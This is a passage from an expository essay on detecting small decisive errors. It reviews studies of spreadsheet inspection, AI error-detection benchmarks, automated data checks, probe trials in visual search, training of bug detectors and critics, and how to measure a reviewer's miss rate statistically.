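This matters when deciding how many people should check something. By the simple formula, five readers would find 99% of the errors. In the illustration they would find only 92%, and nearly all the errors they missed would be the hard kind.

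Teams reviewing program code also seem to find fewer errors than the same number of independent readers would. *Recommended Practices for Spreadsheet Testing* (Panko, 2007) cites an experiment by Johnson and Tjahjono in which individuals found 23% of planted errors and teams of three found 44%. Three independent readers would together have found 54%.

The students' meetings added nothing, so Panko questioned whether they were necessary. Three people could hand in their lists without meeting. Dropping two of the readers to save money would be a mistake, especially since the students were overconfident when they worked alone.

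In *Spreadsheet Presentation and Error Detection*, Galletta, Hartzel and colleagues (1996) gave 113 business students a one-page spreadsheet, also with eight planted errors. The students knew to look for errors but found only about half. Those who read on paper found more than those who read on a screen, but they took longer, which may explain the difference.

Surprisingly, students who could see the formulas did no better than students who saw only the numbers. Readers can see `SUM` in a formula but not in the number 4.8%, and seeing it helps only if they know the formula should contain `AVERAGE`. Perhaps the students rarely worked out what each formula should be. A layout that printed each formula under its result did not help them find errors either, although it seemed to reduce false alarms.

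Experience may not make people much better at finding errors. In an earlier experiment by Galletta's team, which Panko also cites, people found 56% of the errors. Accountants did slightly better than business students, but experienced spreadsheet users did no better than inexperienced ones.

All of these spreadsheets contained many errors. At work, most cells are correct and nobody tells reviewers that something is wrong, so they probably find a smaller share of the errors, as people do in other searches where targets are rare.

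Panko argues against saving effort by reading only the riskiest formulas, because ordinary formulas are much more numerous. Suppose a spreadsheet has 30 complicated formulas, 10% of them wrong, and 970 ordinary ones, 3% of them wrong. The complicated formulas contain 3 errors and the ordinary ones about 29, so an inspector who reads only the complicated ones will miss at least nine errors in ten.

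Software that scans a spreadsheet for suspicious cells is cheap and worth running, but Panko warns that it cannot be expected to detect omissions. If someone forgets to include one of a company's ten main costs, there is no cell to flag. Users also have to judge the warnings. In one experiment, students who used a grammar checker made more grammatical errors than students who did not, because they accepted its wrong suggestions.

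### What AI models found

Thorne (2025), in *Large Language Models for Spreadsheets*, introduced a set of tests called FLARE. In one test, 20 AI models checked a computer-chip factory's simple profit-and-loss spreadsheet, which contained 12 planted errors. Gemini 2.5 Pro found all 12, and ChatGPT 4.5 and o3-mini-high each found 11. Copilot and GPT-4o mini did worst, finding 4 and 2.

The better models were good at noticing faulty formulas, but many models missed errors that look easier to spot, such as a unit price of 50 that should have been 500, or the misspelling "Decemeber". The wrong price can be spotted only by comparing it with the other prices, and Thorne suggests that models may need to be told explicitly to check for consistency and unusual values.

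In a harder test, the models received the formulas from a spreadsheet that classifies triangles. Four of the formulas contained errors. One used `OR` where it needed `AND`, two returned the wrong variable, and one omitted a check that the three sides could form a triangle. A model could earn up to eight points, one for detecting each error and one for fixing it. The best score was 3, and Gemini 2.5 Pro, which had a perfect score on the factory spreadsheet, got 1. No model detected either wrong variable.

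The tests are very small, with one attempt per model, and the scores count only errors found, so models lost no points for false alarms. Still, the harder test is closer to the case where one changed token decides correctness. The price of 50 differs from the values around it, but a formula that returns the wrong side of a triangle looks wrong only when compared with what it is meant to calculate.

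Xi, Rao and colleagues (2025), in *FLAWS*, tested how well models find errors in scientific papers. They had Gemini 2.5 Pro and GPT-5 rewrite passages of published machine-learning papers so that one of each paper's main claims no longer held. This produced 713 altered papers, each with one planted error. Five models then read each paper and listed up to ten suspicious passages, most serious first.

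| Model | Passages usually listed | Error in first passage | In first three | In first ten |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 | 9 | 9.0% | 19.2% | 39.1% |
| DeepSeek Reasoner v3.1 | 9 | 5.9% | 16.3% | 35.2% |
| Grok 4 | 4 or 5 | 8.8% | 16.3% | 23.4% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 5 | 5.2% | 12.6% | 21.5% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 4 | 6.6% | 15.7% | 19.8% |

The last column partly reflects how long each list was. Gemini usually stopped after four passages, so it had fewer chances to be right. The models' results were much closer on their first three passages.

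A longer list also takes more work to check. GPT-5 listed about 8.5 passages per paper, so a reader would have to examine roughly 22 passages for each planted error it found. Some of the other passages may have contained genuine errors from the original papers.

The scores are also low partly because of how Xi and colleagues built the test. They removed easy errors, including any that the model that wrote them could find when it read the altered paper afresh. GPT-5 found 726 of 1,358 errors (53%) at that step, and the researchers discarded them. The 39.1% detection rate therefore covers only errors that had already survived one search. These errors also typically spanned a few sentences, so the result does not show how often GPT-5 would notice a single altered number.

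*Do large language models scrutinise what they review* (Alharbi, August 2026) audited AI peer review using 145 errors planted in 55 papers submitted to a machine-learning conference. Most were small edits, including changes to single numbers. One edit changed "a 2.25× speed-up" in the abstract to "a 2.5× speed-up" while the results still reported 2.25×. Every error contradicted something else in the paper, so a careful reader could have found it without outside knowledge.

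The two reviewers were older open models, Qwen2.5-VL-72B and Pixtral Large. Together they detected 12.1% of the errors when asked for an ordinary review. These are their detection rates for three kinds of error, with the text alone and with the figures included.

| Planted error | Qwen, text | Qwen, with figures | Pixtral, text | Pixtral, with figures |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Invalid statistical claim | 28% | 17% | 67% | 71% |
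| Altered number | 1% | 3% | 36% | 20% |
| Reversed trend | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% |

An example of the first kind is the claim that a method "significantly outperforms" another with a p-value of 0.08, when researchers normally require a value below 0.05. A reader can see that contradiction within one sentence. To find an altered number or a reversed trend, the reader has to remember a figure or claim from the abstract and compare it with a table many pages later. Neither model seems to have done much of this comparison unprompted.

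Telling the models to check the abstract's numbers against the results, and the figures against their descriptions, raised detection to 22.2%, though they still missed more than three-quarters of the errors. The models evidently could make some of these comparisons but did not make them in an ordinary review, much like the programmers who overlooked `"MD5"` until told to look for security issues.

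The models' scores alone would not have warned a reader that a paper was weak. With author names removed, both models gave every group of papers an average score between 7.0 and 8.1 out of 10, including those the conference had clearly rejected. Human reviewers' averages ranged from 3.4 to 6.8.

The models in these three tests are all old by the standards of late 2026, and newer ones probably do better, as they have in code review. The scores are therefore better evidence of which errors are hard to catch than of how many a current model would miss.

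### Checks that do not rely on reading

Some checks compare a number with something more definite than a reader's sense of what looks right. They are especially useful in a *data pipeline*, a series of programs that each convert or combine data and pass it to the next, often without anyone reading the data in between.

| Check | An error it catches | An error it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Recomputation | Someone typed 90,000 over a formula that gives 9,000 | The formula itself is wrong |
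| Control total | A program drops 5 of 1,000 invoices | Two customers' amounts change places |
| Units | A formula adds dollars to thousands of dollars | A formula divides by a sum instead of an average |
| Range limit | A price is 50 when prices run from 400 to 600 | A price is 450 when it should be 540 |
| Second independent calculation | One person used `SUM` and the other `AVERAGE` | Both people misread the same instruction |

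**Recomputation** means repeating a calculation from the same inputs. It exposes an overwritten result but not a wrong formula. Recomputing the JPMorgan formula, for example, would have produced 4.8% every time. Panko recommends a version of this check after changes to a spreadsheet, in which the user re-enters the earlier inputs and compares the final figures with the old ones. This reveals new slips in parts that should not have changed, but not errors that were already there.

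Comparing the result with a known correct answer would be better, but Panko points out that a complex spreadsheet seldom has one, because nobody has done the calculation any other way. A single formula is easier to check like this. If a rate goes from 100 to 102, the change must be close to 2%, but the JPMorgan formula would have given 1%.

A **control total** is a count or sum that someone records at the start and compares with the data after each step. If 1,000 invoices enter a pipeline and 995 come out, the pipeline has lost five. A count of the countries in the Reinhart and Rogoff average would have exposed the missing rows. But if the pipeline swaps two customers' charges of $540 and $450, the count and the sum stay the same.

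When a total does disagree, the size of the difference can suggest the cause. Swapping two neighbouring digits always changes a whole number by a multiple of 9, because

$$(10a + b) - (10b + a) = 9(a - b)$$

If a total is off by a multiple of 9, someone may have swapped two digits or misplaced a decimal point. Typing 450 for 540 makes the total 90 too low. Moving a decimal point one place to the right adds nine times the original number, so turning an interest charge of 9,000 into 90,000 makes the total 81,000 too high. This is only a hint, because about one difference in nine is a multiple of 9 by chance.

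**A unit check** tests whether the quantities in a formula have compatible units. It catches a monthly rate multiplied by a number of years. It would have missed the error in the JPMorgan formula, because the sum of two rates has the same units as their average.

**A range limit** rejects values outside fixed bounds. A 20% limit on interest rates would catch a 4.5% rate changed to 45%, but not one changed to 5.4%. Narrower bounds would catch more errors but raise more false alarms.

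An outlier check is more flexible because it compares each value with the rest of its column. A common version measures how far a value x lies from the column's average m, in units of the column's standard deviation s:

$$z = \frac{x - m}{s}$$

If prices average 500 with a standard deviation of 20, a z-score check flags a price of 50 (z = −22.5) but passes a price of 480 (z = −1), whether or not 480 is correct.

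The check would not have caught the JPMorgan error, because halving every value in a column also halves its average and standard deviation, which leaves every z the same. Comparing the new model's results with the old model's could have revealed the drop, but people expect a new model to give different results.

**A second independent calculation** takes the most work of these checks, and is the only one in the table that would probably have caught the JPMorgan error. Someone else builds the calculation from the written description and the original data, without looking at the first version. If two people each make an error in 5% of such calculations, and their errors are independent, both will be wrong only 0.25% of the time, and seldom in the same way. But if the description misleads everyone 1% of the time, it will cause most of the wrong answers they agree on.

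In FLARE, Thorne asked AI models to work out the price of building a wall from a written brief. Sixteen models gave the correct price for the granite version, £1,934.40. Mistral's model and an older GPT-4 both gave £2,683.20, and they also gave the same wrong price for the brick version. Two models from different companies are unlikely to match to the penny by accident, so they very probably made the same mistake. A company that used one to check the other would have found no discrepancy.

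The second person therefore should not start from a copy of the first spreadsheet or ask its creator how the formula works. At JPMorgan, someone who built their own spreadsheet from a description that said "average" would have got exactly twice the bank's figure in every row. Because the difference was so regular, they would have traced it to the denominator fairly quickly.

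## Training people and models to notice small changes

A second independent calculation would probably have exposed the JPMorgan error, but few organisations can afford to do all their work twice. Most work gets one reader, so it matters whether training can help that reader catch more errors. Psychologists have tried to help people find rare targets, and computer scientists have trained models to find bugs. Both groups find it hard to judge their results, because a reviewer who catches more errors after training may simply be flagging more of everything, including correct work.

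### Bursts, decoys and false feedback

Many attempts to remove the low-prevalence effect, people's tendency to miss targets because they are rare, have failed. *Reducing the low-prevalence effect with probe trials* (Becker, Rodriguez and colleagues, 2026) lists several. Making people wait before they could answer did not remove the effect, and neither did an eye tracker that showed them which parts of the display they had yet to look at. Requiring people to point to the item that most resembled the target did remove it, and when a target was present they often chose it. But with this instruction people choose an item in every display, even when no target is present, and when another team also asked whether the chosen item really was a target, the effect returned.

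A more successful remedy is to make targets common for a while. *Comparing Breast Screening Protocols* (Chen and Howe, 2016) describes an experiment in which Jeremy Wolfe's team had people search 1,000 X-ray images of luggage. Only 2% contained a target, and people got no feedback. Among these images the researchers inserted ten bursts of 40 in which half contained a target and people learned the answer each time. People then missed rare targets at no higher a rate than common ones. They also raised more false alarms, and discriminability (d') stayed about the same, so the bursts shifted the criterion without making people better at recognising targets.

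Bursts did raise d' in two later experiments, one with specialists who examine cells for signs of cervical cancer and the other with baggage screeners. Chen and Howe suggest that rarity lowers d' for only some kinds of image, and that a burst raises d' only where rarity has lowered it. In either case the benefit fades within a few dozen images, so reviewers would need bursts often.

False feedback has a similar effect on the criterion. Peltier and Becker (2017), in *Individual differences predict low prevalence visual search performance*, describe an experiment in which participants were told, after 20% of their correct "no target" responses, that they had missed one. The participants found more targets and raised more false alarms, as did the volunteers whom Kunar and colleagues misled about missed tumours.

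Wolfe's team also tried adding a common object to the search. A water bottle that appeared in 44% of images did not help people find a gun that appeared in 1%. But when the target was any kind of tool, a common tool did help people find a rare one.

### Probe trials

A *probe trial* is a case with a known target, mixed into real work and usually followed by feedback. Many countries require something similar at airports, where the X-ray system adds a fake weapon to the image of a real bag and notifies the screener afterwards. The airport version is used mainly for training and monitoring, and its performance data are classified.

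Becker and colleagues tested whether probes also help people find real targets. In their first experiment, 102 students looked for a T among L shapes in 250 displays, 10% of which contained a T. Adding 50 displays with a known T, spread throughout the task, raised the detection rate. A single burst of 50 displays, half of them with a T, worked about as well.

In the second experiment, 160 students looked for either a T or an O. The more often a letter appeared in the probes, the more its detection rate rose, and the rate didn't improve for a letter that never appeared in them. A later experiment with 81 people used one letter in 80% of the probes and the other in 20%. Detection of the more frequent letter rose from 70.5% without probes to 78.9% with them. Detection of the other letter rose from 66.9% to 69.9%, which could have been chance. Probes helped even without feedback, so most of the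 benefit seems to come from seeing the target more often.

It is harder to say whether the probes raised discriminability. People raised false alarms on fewer than 2% of displays, too few for the researchers to calculate d'. Becker and colleagues saw no increase in false alarms and infer that discriminability probably rose, but a tiny increase would undermine that inference. Across both letters, the detection rate rose from 68.7% to 74.4%. If the false-alarm rate had also risen from 1.5% to 2.3%, which is about one more false alarm per person in 120 displays, d' would not have changed.

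An eye-tracking experiment gives better evidence of a real gain. With probes, the share of targets that people never looked at fell from 17.8% to 12.5%, even though people looked at about as many items before giving up. The share they looked at but still missed did not change reliably. The probes therefore seem to have drawn people's eyes towards shapes like the ones they had been seeing, without making them more willing to call a shape a target.

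If the same is true of code, probes will help only with the kinds of error they contain. Reviewers who often see planted `<=` errors might check comparisons more carefully but still overlook a missing input check, because there is nothing on the page to spot. A team that plants errors should probably vary them, and should tell reviewers which ones they missed. Without feedback, people in the letter experiment overlooked about 30% of the probes, and those missed probes could not make targets seem more common.

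### Catch trials or a second reader

Adding a second reader is the most obvious remedy, but it is expensive, and both readers tend to miss the same targets. Becker and colleagues cite one experiment in which a second reader reduced the low-prevalence effect and another in which it did not.

In the Australian state of Victoria, two radiologists read every mammogram, and if they disagree, a third decides. Chen and Howe tested having one person read each image and using the time saved to show extra images that always contained a target, with feedback. These *catch trials* raised the share of images with a target from 4% to 44%. Other people then checked whatever the single reader had flagged.

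Each of their two experiments involved 34 people, mostly students. In the more realistic one, participants looked for faint discs with blurred edges, which imitated malignant tumours. The catch trials probably raised the detection rate, but the false-alarm rate nearly tripled, to about 20%, and d' was no higher than with two readers. The other experiment, which used letters, gave only weak evidence of a higher d'. Chen and Howe concluded that they could not recommend a clinical trial.

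Comparing a single reader given catch trials with double reading was a demanding test of the catch trials, because a second reader might find a target the first had missed. The catch trials made up for the lack of a second reader, but apparently by getting people to flag more. That could still be worthwhile where false alarms are easy to dismiss, for example when a programmer can check with a quick test.

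An organisation could also choose its reviewers by testing them. Peltier and Becker gave 141 students a search task in which 10% of the displays contained a target, and scored them by their detection rate minus their false-alarm rate. The best predictor of this score was performance on the same task with targets in half of the displays (a correlation of 0.67). Testing with common targets is more practical, because measuring someone's performance with very rare targets takes thousands of displays. Performance with common targets, together with visual memory, vigilance, control of attention and introversion, accounted for more than half of the variation in scores between people. However, the experiment did not test people on reading code.

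### Artificial bugs and real ones

Models usually need far more examples than people do, and real bugs are scarce. Researchers therefore often train models on artificial bugs, made in much the same way as mutants. In *On Distribution Shift in Learning-based Bug Detectors*, He, Beurer-Kellner and Vechev (2022) showed that such models can do poorly on real code. They studied errors of one or a few tokens in Python functions, such as a wrong variable or operator.

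A model trained on artificial wrong-variable errors was almost perfect on a test set of the same kind. When the researchers replaced the artificial errors in the test with real ones, its detection rate fell by 56 percentage points. They then added a large amount of correct code, as in real projects, and its precision fell to 3%. The first drop suggests that real errors differ from artificial ones. The second occurred mostly because errors made up a much smaller share of the test set.

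He et al. therefore trained a model in two phases. It learned first from about 150,000 artificial bugs of each type and their correct versions, then from a few hundred real bugs among roughly 100,000 correct functions. The counts and d' in this table follow from the published rates.

| Error | Training | Errors found | False alarms | Precision | d' |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Wrong variable | Artificial only | 119 of 336 | about 3,350 | 3% | 1.2 |
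| Wrong variable | Artificial, then real | 46 of 336 | about 25 | 65% | 2.3 |
| Wrong operator | Artificial only | 241 of 491 | about 2,250 | 10% | 1.6 |
| Wrong operator | Artificial, then real | 216 of 491 | about 200 | 52% | 2.4 |

The second phase made the model much more cautious, and it found far fewer of the wrong variables. But d' rose for both types of error, so the model had also got better at separating faulty functions from sound ones. Both phases were necessary. Trained only on real bugs, the model never flagged a wrong variable. When the researchers mixed real and artificial bugs in one phase, the artificial ones swamped the real ones and precision stayed low.

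The 52% precision for wrong operators is less impressive than it looks. When He and colleagues scanned current projects and read 100 of these warnings, only 6 identified bugs. Another 80 were about coding style that rarely causes trouble. The model had learned to flag these cases because the collection of real bugs contained similar ones. After the researchers filtered out such warnings, 37 of a second set of 100 identified bugs.

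### Training on near-identical pairs

He and colleagues also penalised the model for representing a program and its altered copy too similarly. Dropping the penalty lowered precision by 4 or 5 percentage points. Lu, Rostami Mazrae and Lagaisse (2026) extend this idea in *PatchCon*, using real security flaws from the Linux kernel and their fixes.

PatchCon uses CodeBERT, a small language model for code, to turn each function into a list of numbers. The similarity of two functions ranges from −1 to 1, reaching 1 when their lists point in the same direction. A faulty function and its corrected version share most of their text, so they tend to be very similar before training. Researchers call such a pair a *hard negative*, meaning two similar items that the model must learn to separate.

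The model learns from four kinds of pair: two sound functions, two faulty ones, a faulty and a sound function that are unrelated, and a faulty function with its own fix. Training adjusts the model to reduce a number called the loss:

$$L = L_{\text{label}} + \lambda\,(L_{\text{together}} + L_{\text{apart}})$$

The first term, L_label, is the usual penalty for labelling a function wrongly. The second applies to every function i whose partner p has the same label:

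$$L_{\text{together}} = \text{average of } -\log\frac{e^{s_{ip}/\tau}}{\sum_{a \neq i} e^{s_{ia}/\tau}}$$

The sum covers all the other functions in the current batch. This penalty is small when a function is much more similar to its partner than to the rest. The third term applies to pairs with different labels:

$$L_{\text{apart}} = \text{average of } w \log\left(1 + e^{(s-m)/\tau}\right)$$

This penalty is close to zero when s is well below the margin m, and it rises steadily once s is above it. The weight w is 2 for a function and its own fix and 1 for an unrelated pair. With an illustrative margin of 0.5 and the researchers' setting of τ = 0.07, the penalty for a function and its fix with a similarity of 0.9 is 11.4. An unrelated pair at the same similarity would have half that penalty, and at a similarity of 0.2 both penalties would be close to zero. Lu and colleagues set λ to 0.01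 so that labelling remains the main goal.

They tested the result on 432 pairs. For comparison, the table includes CodeBERT, trained in the ordinary way, and DELTA, an earlier method that also learns from flaws and their fixes but gives them no extra weight. The d' values are calculated from the other columns.

| Method | Correct | Reversed | Both flagged | Both cleared | d' |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
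| CodeBERT | 5% | 1% | 88% | 6% | 0.2 |
| DELTA | 21% | 6% | 47% | 27% | 0.4 |
| PatchCon | 33% | 12% | 28% | 27% | 0.5 |

PatchCon judged 12 percentage points more pairs correctly than DELTA, but it also reversed twice as many, so its lead in correct minus reversed pairs is only 6 points. Their scores on a measure of overall classification skill differed by less than the margin of error. Part of PatchCon's improvement over ordinary CodeBERT comes from flagging 51% of functions instead of 91%, because random guessing also gets more pairs correct at the lower rate.

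PatchCon did particularly well on small changes. It got 33% right of the 195 pairs in which the fix changed only one or two lines, compared with 19% for DELTA. A fix that added the condition `|| set->dead` lowered PatchCon's suspicion score from 0.74 to 0.26, but the score stayed above 0.99 when another fix added a missing check for a failed memory request.

The extra weight seems to help, since setting w to 1 lowered the share of correct pairs to 27%. But the researchers trained each version only once, and setting w to 1.5 did no better than setting it to 1, so some of these differences may be luck.

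The results on new flaws are less encouraging. Lu and colleagues tested 111 pairs from flaws published in May 2025, more than a year after the newest flaw in the training data, and advise caution about such a small set. PatchCon got the most pairs right, with 18, but it reversed 12, a difference that could easily be chance. DELTA got 14 right and reversed only 2, which is better evidence that it could tell the versions apart. Lu and colleagues did not test PatchCon on ordinary sound functions, so its precision in everyday use is unknown.

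### Choosing which lines to judge

*Learning to Focus* (Zheng, Qian and colleagues, 2025) introduces FocusVul, a system that removes irrelevant code before a model judges the rest. A small model first learns which lines were changed in thousands of past fixes, so that it can pick out similar lines in a function nobody has fixed. During training, the researchers hide some of the words at random so that the model doesn't simply memorise suspicious ones such as `NULL`. Ordinary software then adds neighbouring code and any lines that affect the selected lines or are affected by them. A second model sees only this shortened function and decides whether it is faulty.

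Zheng and colleagues trained four models with and without this step and tested them on pairs from PrimeVul. The share of pairs the models got right rose from 1–7% to 19–28%, and they reversed fewer than 2% of pairs. CodeBERT's d', inferred from these figures, rose from about 0.2 to 0.9, so its gain did not come only from a change in how often it flagged functions. The much larger general-purpose models that Cichoń and Dmitruk tested got 7–18% of PrimeVul's pairs right.

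FocusVul also helped on a large test set in which most functions were sound. With it, CodeBERT's precision rose from 25% to 53%, and the share of flaws it detected rose from 14% to 33%.

Selecting the wrong lines can be worse than giving the model the whole function. When the researchers replaced the trained selector with fixed rules during testing, CodeBERT did slightly worse than when it read whole functions. Even with the trained selector, only 73% of the relevant text remained after shortening and a length limit, compared with 62% when long functions were just cut off at the limit. If the selector drops the decisive token, the second model cannot detect it.

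### Critics trained on inserted bugs

People can also write the artificial bugs. *LLM Critics Help Catch LLM Bugs* (McAleese, Pokorny et al., 2024) describes how OpenAI used such bugs to train CriticGPT, a model that commented on code written by ChatGPT. Paid programmers inserted subtle bugs into ChatGPT's answers and described each one as if they had caught it in a review. They were supposed to check that an existing AI critic missed the bug at least once in three attempts. The programmers then ranked several critiques of the altered code, and the researchers trained CriticGPT to write critiques that would rank highly.

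The descriptions gave the programmers a definite standard for judging critiques. When the code had no known bug, they often disagreed about which critique was better, and critics trained only on unaltered code did much worse.

CriticGPT caught far more inserted bugs than programmers from the same pool, who had a median of five years' Python experience and spent about 50 minutes on each review. ChatGPT without the special training also caught more than the programmers did. Raters preferred CriticGPT's critiques to human ones 63% of the time for ChatGPT's own bugs and more than 80% of the time for inserted bugs.

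CriticGPT also invented problems more often than people did. The more claims a critique contained, the more likely it was to include both the real bug and a false one, so writing longer critiques is much like lowering the criterion. The researchers could control this by generating many candidate critiques and changing how much they favoured the longer ones. Programmers who started with CriticGPT's comments and edited them caught about as many bugs as CriticGPT did alone but made fewer false claims. This was better than any of those settings achieved, so editing improved discriminability rather than just moving the criterion.

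The researchers also ran CriticGPT on ChatGPT training answers that a first rater had called flawless, most of which were not code. When CriticGPT identified a problem, a second rater agreed 24% of the time that it was serious. Without a critique, second raters marked down only 6% of such answers. Some of the difference may be due to CriticGPT's comments swaying the raters.

The gap between artificial and real bugs affected CriticGPT too. The inserted bugs were more severe and harder to find than the ones ChatGPT made itself, and CriticGPT learned to ignore kinds of errors that were rare among the inserted bugs. An early version also gave no significant help on a task that resembles the pair test. People saw two solutions to a hard programming problem, one right and one wrong, and had 20 minutes to choose the right one without running the code.

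Later reviewers have overcome some of CriticGPT's limits. CriticGPT saw only short pieces of code. In 2025 Trębacz, one of its creators, described a newer OpenAI reviewer that can read a whole project and run the code. McAleese and colleagues also suggested having models insert the bugs, because those bugs might look more like the errors models make on their own. Models now plant many errors, including those in CLAUSE and FLAWS, but these are used to test reviewers rather than train them.

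In 2026, Wang and colleagues used past bugs to produce mutants that resemble real bugs more closely than earlier mutants did. They compared the mutants by which tests they failed, so their results do not show whether a detector trained on them would stay precise on real code. Experiments by He and colleagues give more direct evidence, which supports finishing the training with real errors among a realistic amount of correct code.

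## Measuring how many decisive changes a reviewer misses

The wrong-variable detector that He and colleagues trained on artificial bugs was nearly perfect on artificial bugs but not on real ones, so a test needs as much care as the training. According to *Keep calm and carry on*, researchers planted nine major errors in each of three papers and sent them to peer reviewers of the BMJ, a medical journal. The average reviewer found about three of the nine errors, or slightly fewer.

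A miss rate is hard to interpret without knowing how difficult the errors were to spot, or how often the same reviewers objected to correct passages.

### Choosing the errors

Planted errors should resemble the ones the reviewer will meet at work. Panko's *Improving Methodology in Spreadsheet Error Research* advises researchers to avoid planted errors and instead use mistakes that people made while building spreadsheets in earlier experiments. Real mistakes are better where a collection of them exists, but decisive changes are rare and most collections contain only the errors somebody noticed. *PROBE* (2026) found that AI coding agents catch different bugs from the ones a project's maintainers fix, so a test built from past fixes may also leave out much of what a reviewer could catch.

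A reviewer's score depends largely on how difficult the errors are. Litvak (2026), in *How Well Does AI Peer Review Work?*, planted errors in ten psychology papers. The first set was too easy to be useful, so Litvak made harder ones, many of them by deleting information instead of inserting a mistake. The best AI system found 71 of the final 100 errors. The same system would have scored higher on the first set.

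Zubeldia, Bolliet and colleagues (2026), in *Auditing AI peer reviewers*, dealt with this by planting errors at three levels of subtlety and reporting each level separately. For numbers, a subtle error was a change in the second decimal place between the abstract and the body of the paper, a clear one was two swapped digits, and a blatant one was a set of percentages that added up to more than 100. They planted 357 errors in 30 papers, all newer than the training data of the models they tested. A model that has already seen the original paper may recognise an altered number from memory, which would not help it review new work.

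Somebody then has to confirm that each planted change makes the output wrong. Some changes make no difference, like the equivalent mutants that no test can detect, and answer keys contain mistakes. *The Answer Is Not the Argument* (2026) closely reviewed 99 physics questions from a difficult AI exam and found 16 with a reference answer that was incorrect or physically impossible. *Top Score on the Wrong Exam* (Risse, Liu and Böhme, 2024) checked 300 functions that three popular collections labelled as vulnerable and found that only 39% to 65% were, depending on the collection. The checking took two security researchers more than 150 hours, which may be why so few people do it.

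The reviewer must also be able to detect the error from the material provided. Risse and colleagues confirmed 151 real vulnerabilities, none of which could be identified with certainty from the function alone. In a typical case, a function divides by a number it receives, so it crashes only if another part of the program can pass it a zero. They also took 90 functions labelled as safe and could invent surrounding code that would make 82 of them vulnerable.

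A simple precaution is to show a colleague the error, along with exactly the material the reviewer will receive, and ask them to demonstrate that it is an error. They could do this with an input that produces the wrong result, a clause that contradicts the altered one, or a trusted record that differs. If they can't, the error does not belong in the test.

### Including sound items

A reviewer can score well on a test by flagging everything if there are no sound items, or by using irrelevant clues if the sound items are poorly chosen. Risse and colleagues trained a simple classifier to detect vulnerable functions using only how often each word appeared in them. On one popular dataset it reached an F1 of 0.86, compared with 0.96 for the best published method. Word counts do not record what the code does, so the classifier must have learned that some words are more common in functions labelled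 vulnerable.

Matched pairs, as in the pair test, remove most of these clues, but not code length. If a language model wrote the planted errors, the same model should also make harmless edits to the correct copies. Otherwise a reviewer could score well by noticing that a copy had been edited.

Many published tests don't measure false alarms on clean papers. Zubeldia and colleagues compared 11 earlier AI review systems and benchmarks and found only one that did so fully.

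A high detection rate is less impressive when it comes with many false alarms. *A semi-autonomous multi-agent pipeline for high-energy astrophysics research* (2026) describes automatic checks on AI-written scientific code. The checks stopped 64 of 65 planted defects but also produced 113 false rejections. The test had only 69 sound changes, so the checks must have rejected some of them more than once.

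But most of those objections identified real weaknesses in the code or its tests. A program is usually labelled "sound" only because nobody planted an error in it. In *What Moves the Ceiling on Automated Audit* (2026), an AI reviewer flagged 20 of 150 programs that had passed all their tests. When the researchers ran the inputs the reviewer had complained about, two programs gave a different result from the reference solution, on inputs the tests had never tried, and nine gave the same result. The complaints about the other nine contained no usable input. Someone should therefore read at least a sample of the apparent false alarms before counting them against the reviewer.

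### Fixing the time, the instructions and the number of guesses

Panko asks researchers to report how long inspectors spent, since people who read longer tend to find more. For an AI reviewer, the instructions can matter as much. Zubeldia and colleagues tested models with a one-sentence request for a referee's report, then again with 978 lines of detailed instructions. On the astrophysics papers, Gemini 3.1 Pro's detection rate rose from 12% to 37%, while GPT-5.5's rose only from 60.5% to 61.3%. Someone who tested only with the short request would have concluded that GPT-5.5 was five times as good as Gemini, but with the detailed instructions its detection rate was less than twice Gemini's.

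Litvak did not limit the number of guesses, which matters because a reviewer that lists enough suspicions will eventually include the right one. These are four of the 11 results, with the last column calculated from the other two.

| System | Planted errors found | Comments written | Comments per error found |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.5, high reasoning | 71 | 512 | 7.2 |
| GPT-5.5, no reasoning | 66 | 704 | 10.7 |
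| Claude Opus 4.8, with thinking | 52 | 227 | 4.4 |
| Reviewer3, a commercial tool | 30 | 125 | 4.2 |

Reviewer3 came last in the ranking but needed the fewest comments per planted error of any system. GPT-5.5 without reasoning wrote about 70 comments on each paper. Litvak did not check the comments that matched no planted error, so many of them may have been correct. But an author who has time to read only ten comments learns little from a detection rate based on 70. Limiting each system to its ten most serious comments would have made the comparison more useful. Another option is to report what *LLM-based Code Auditing by Inferring and Evaluating Developer Assumptions* (2026) calls *overhead*, the average number of findings a person must examine before confirming a known flaw.

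Finally, the reviewer should have to say where the error is and what is wrong. Xi and colleagues describe an earlier test in which Dycke and Gurevych inserted logical errors into papers and measured whether AI reviewers then paid more attention to the papers' soundness. A reviewer could pass that test without identifying the error. In the astrophysics test, the AI that reviewed the code made 46 of the rejections. A language model compared the stated reason for each with the planted defect and found that 44 matched. In the other two cases, the AI rejected defective code by luck, and a programmer who followed its stated reason would have repaired the wrong thing.

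### How many planted errors a claim needs

A reviewer who finds all 300 errors in a test may still have a true miss rate above zero. Someone who misses 1% of such errors has about a 5% chance (0.99^300) of finding all 300. So the result is good evidence that the miss rate is below about 1%, but poor evidence that it is below 0.1%.

To get the general rule, find the miss rate m at which a perfect score on n errors would have only a 5% chance:

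$$(1-m)^n = 0.05 \quad\Rightarrow\quad m = 1 - 0.05^{1/n} \approx \frac{3}{n}$$

If a reviewer misses none of the n decisive changes in a test, the miss rate is below 3/n at 95% confidence. Statisticians call this the *rule of three*. In *Probability of adverse events that have not yet occurred*, Eypasch, Lefering and colleagues (1995) recommended the rule, for n above 30, to surgeons reporting operations without complications. A surgeon with 30 such operations can rule out only complication rates above about 10%.

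The rule applies only when the reviewer catches every error. If the reviewer misses a few, a test can still support the claim that the miss rate is below 1%, but it has to be larger.

| Misses in the test | Planted errors needed to support a miss rate below 1% |
|---|---|
| 0 | 299 |
| 1 | 473 |
| 2 | 628 |
| 3 | 773 |

The tester must choose the number of errors in advance, because someone who adds more after each miss until the results support the claim will find support for it too often.

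The errors must also be independent trials. Testing 100 errors three times each does not give 300 independent trials, and neither does planting 300 errors in three documents, because a reviewer who misunderstands one document may miss every error in it. *We Fixed the Scorer First* (2026) reports a first analysis that treated 24 trials of AI code review as independent and found a significant difference in how many planted defects two set-ups caught (p = 0.019). The difference was no longer significant after a correction for clustering, which allows for related trials having similar results.

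Even 300 independent trials only support claims about errors like those tested. Suppose every trial tested a wrong operator, but only 90% of errors in real work are wrong operators. The other 10% are omissions, and the reviewer misses half of them. If the reviewer misses 1% of wrong operators, the overall miss rate is 5.9% (0.9 × 1% + 0.1 × 50%), and most of the missed errors are omissions, which the test didn't include.

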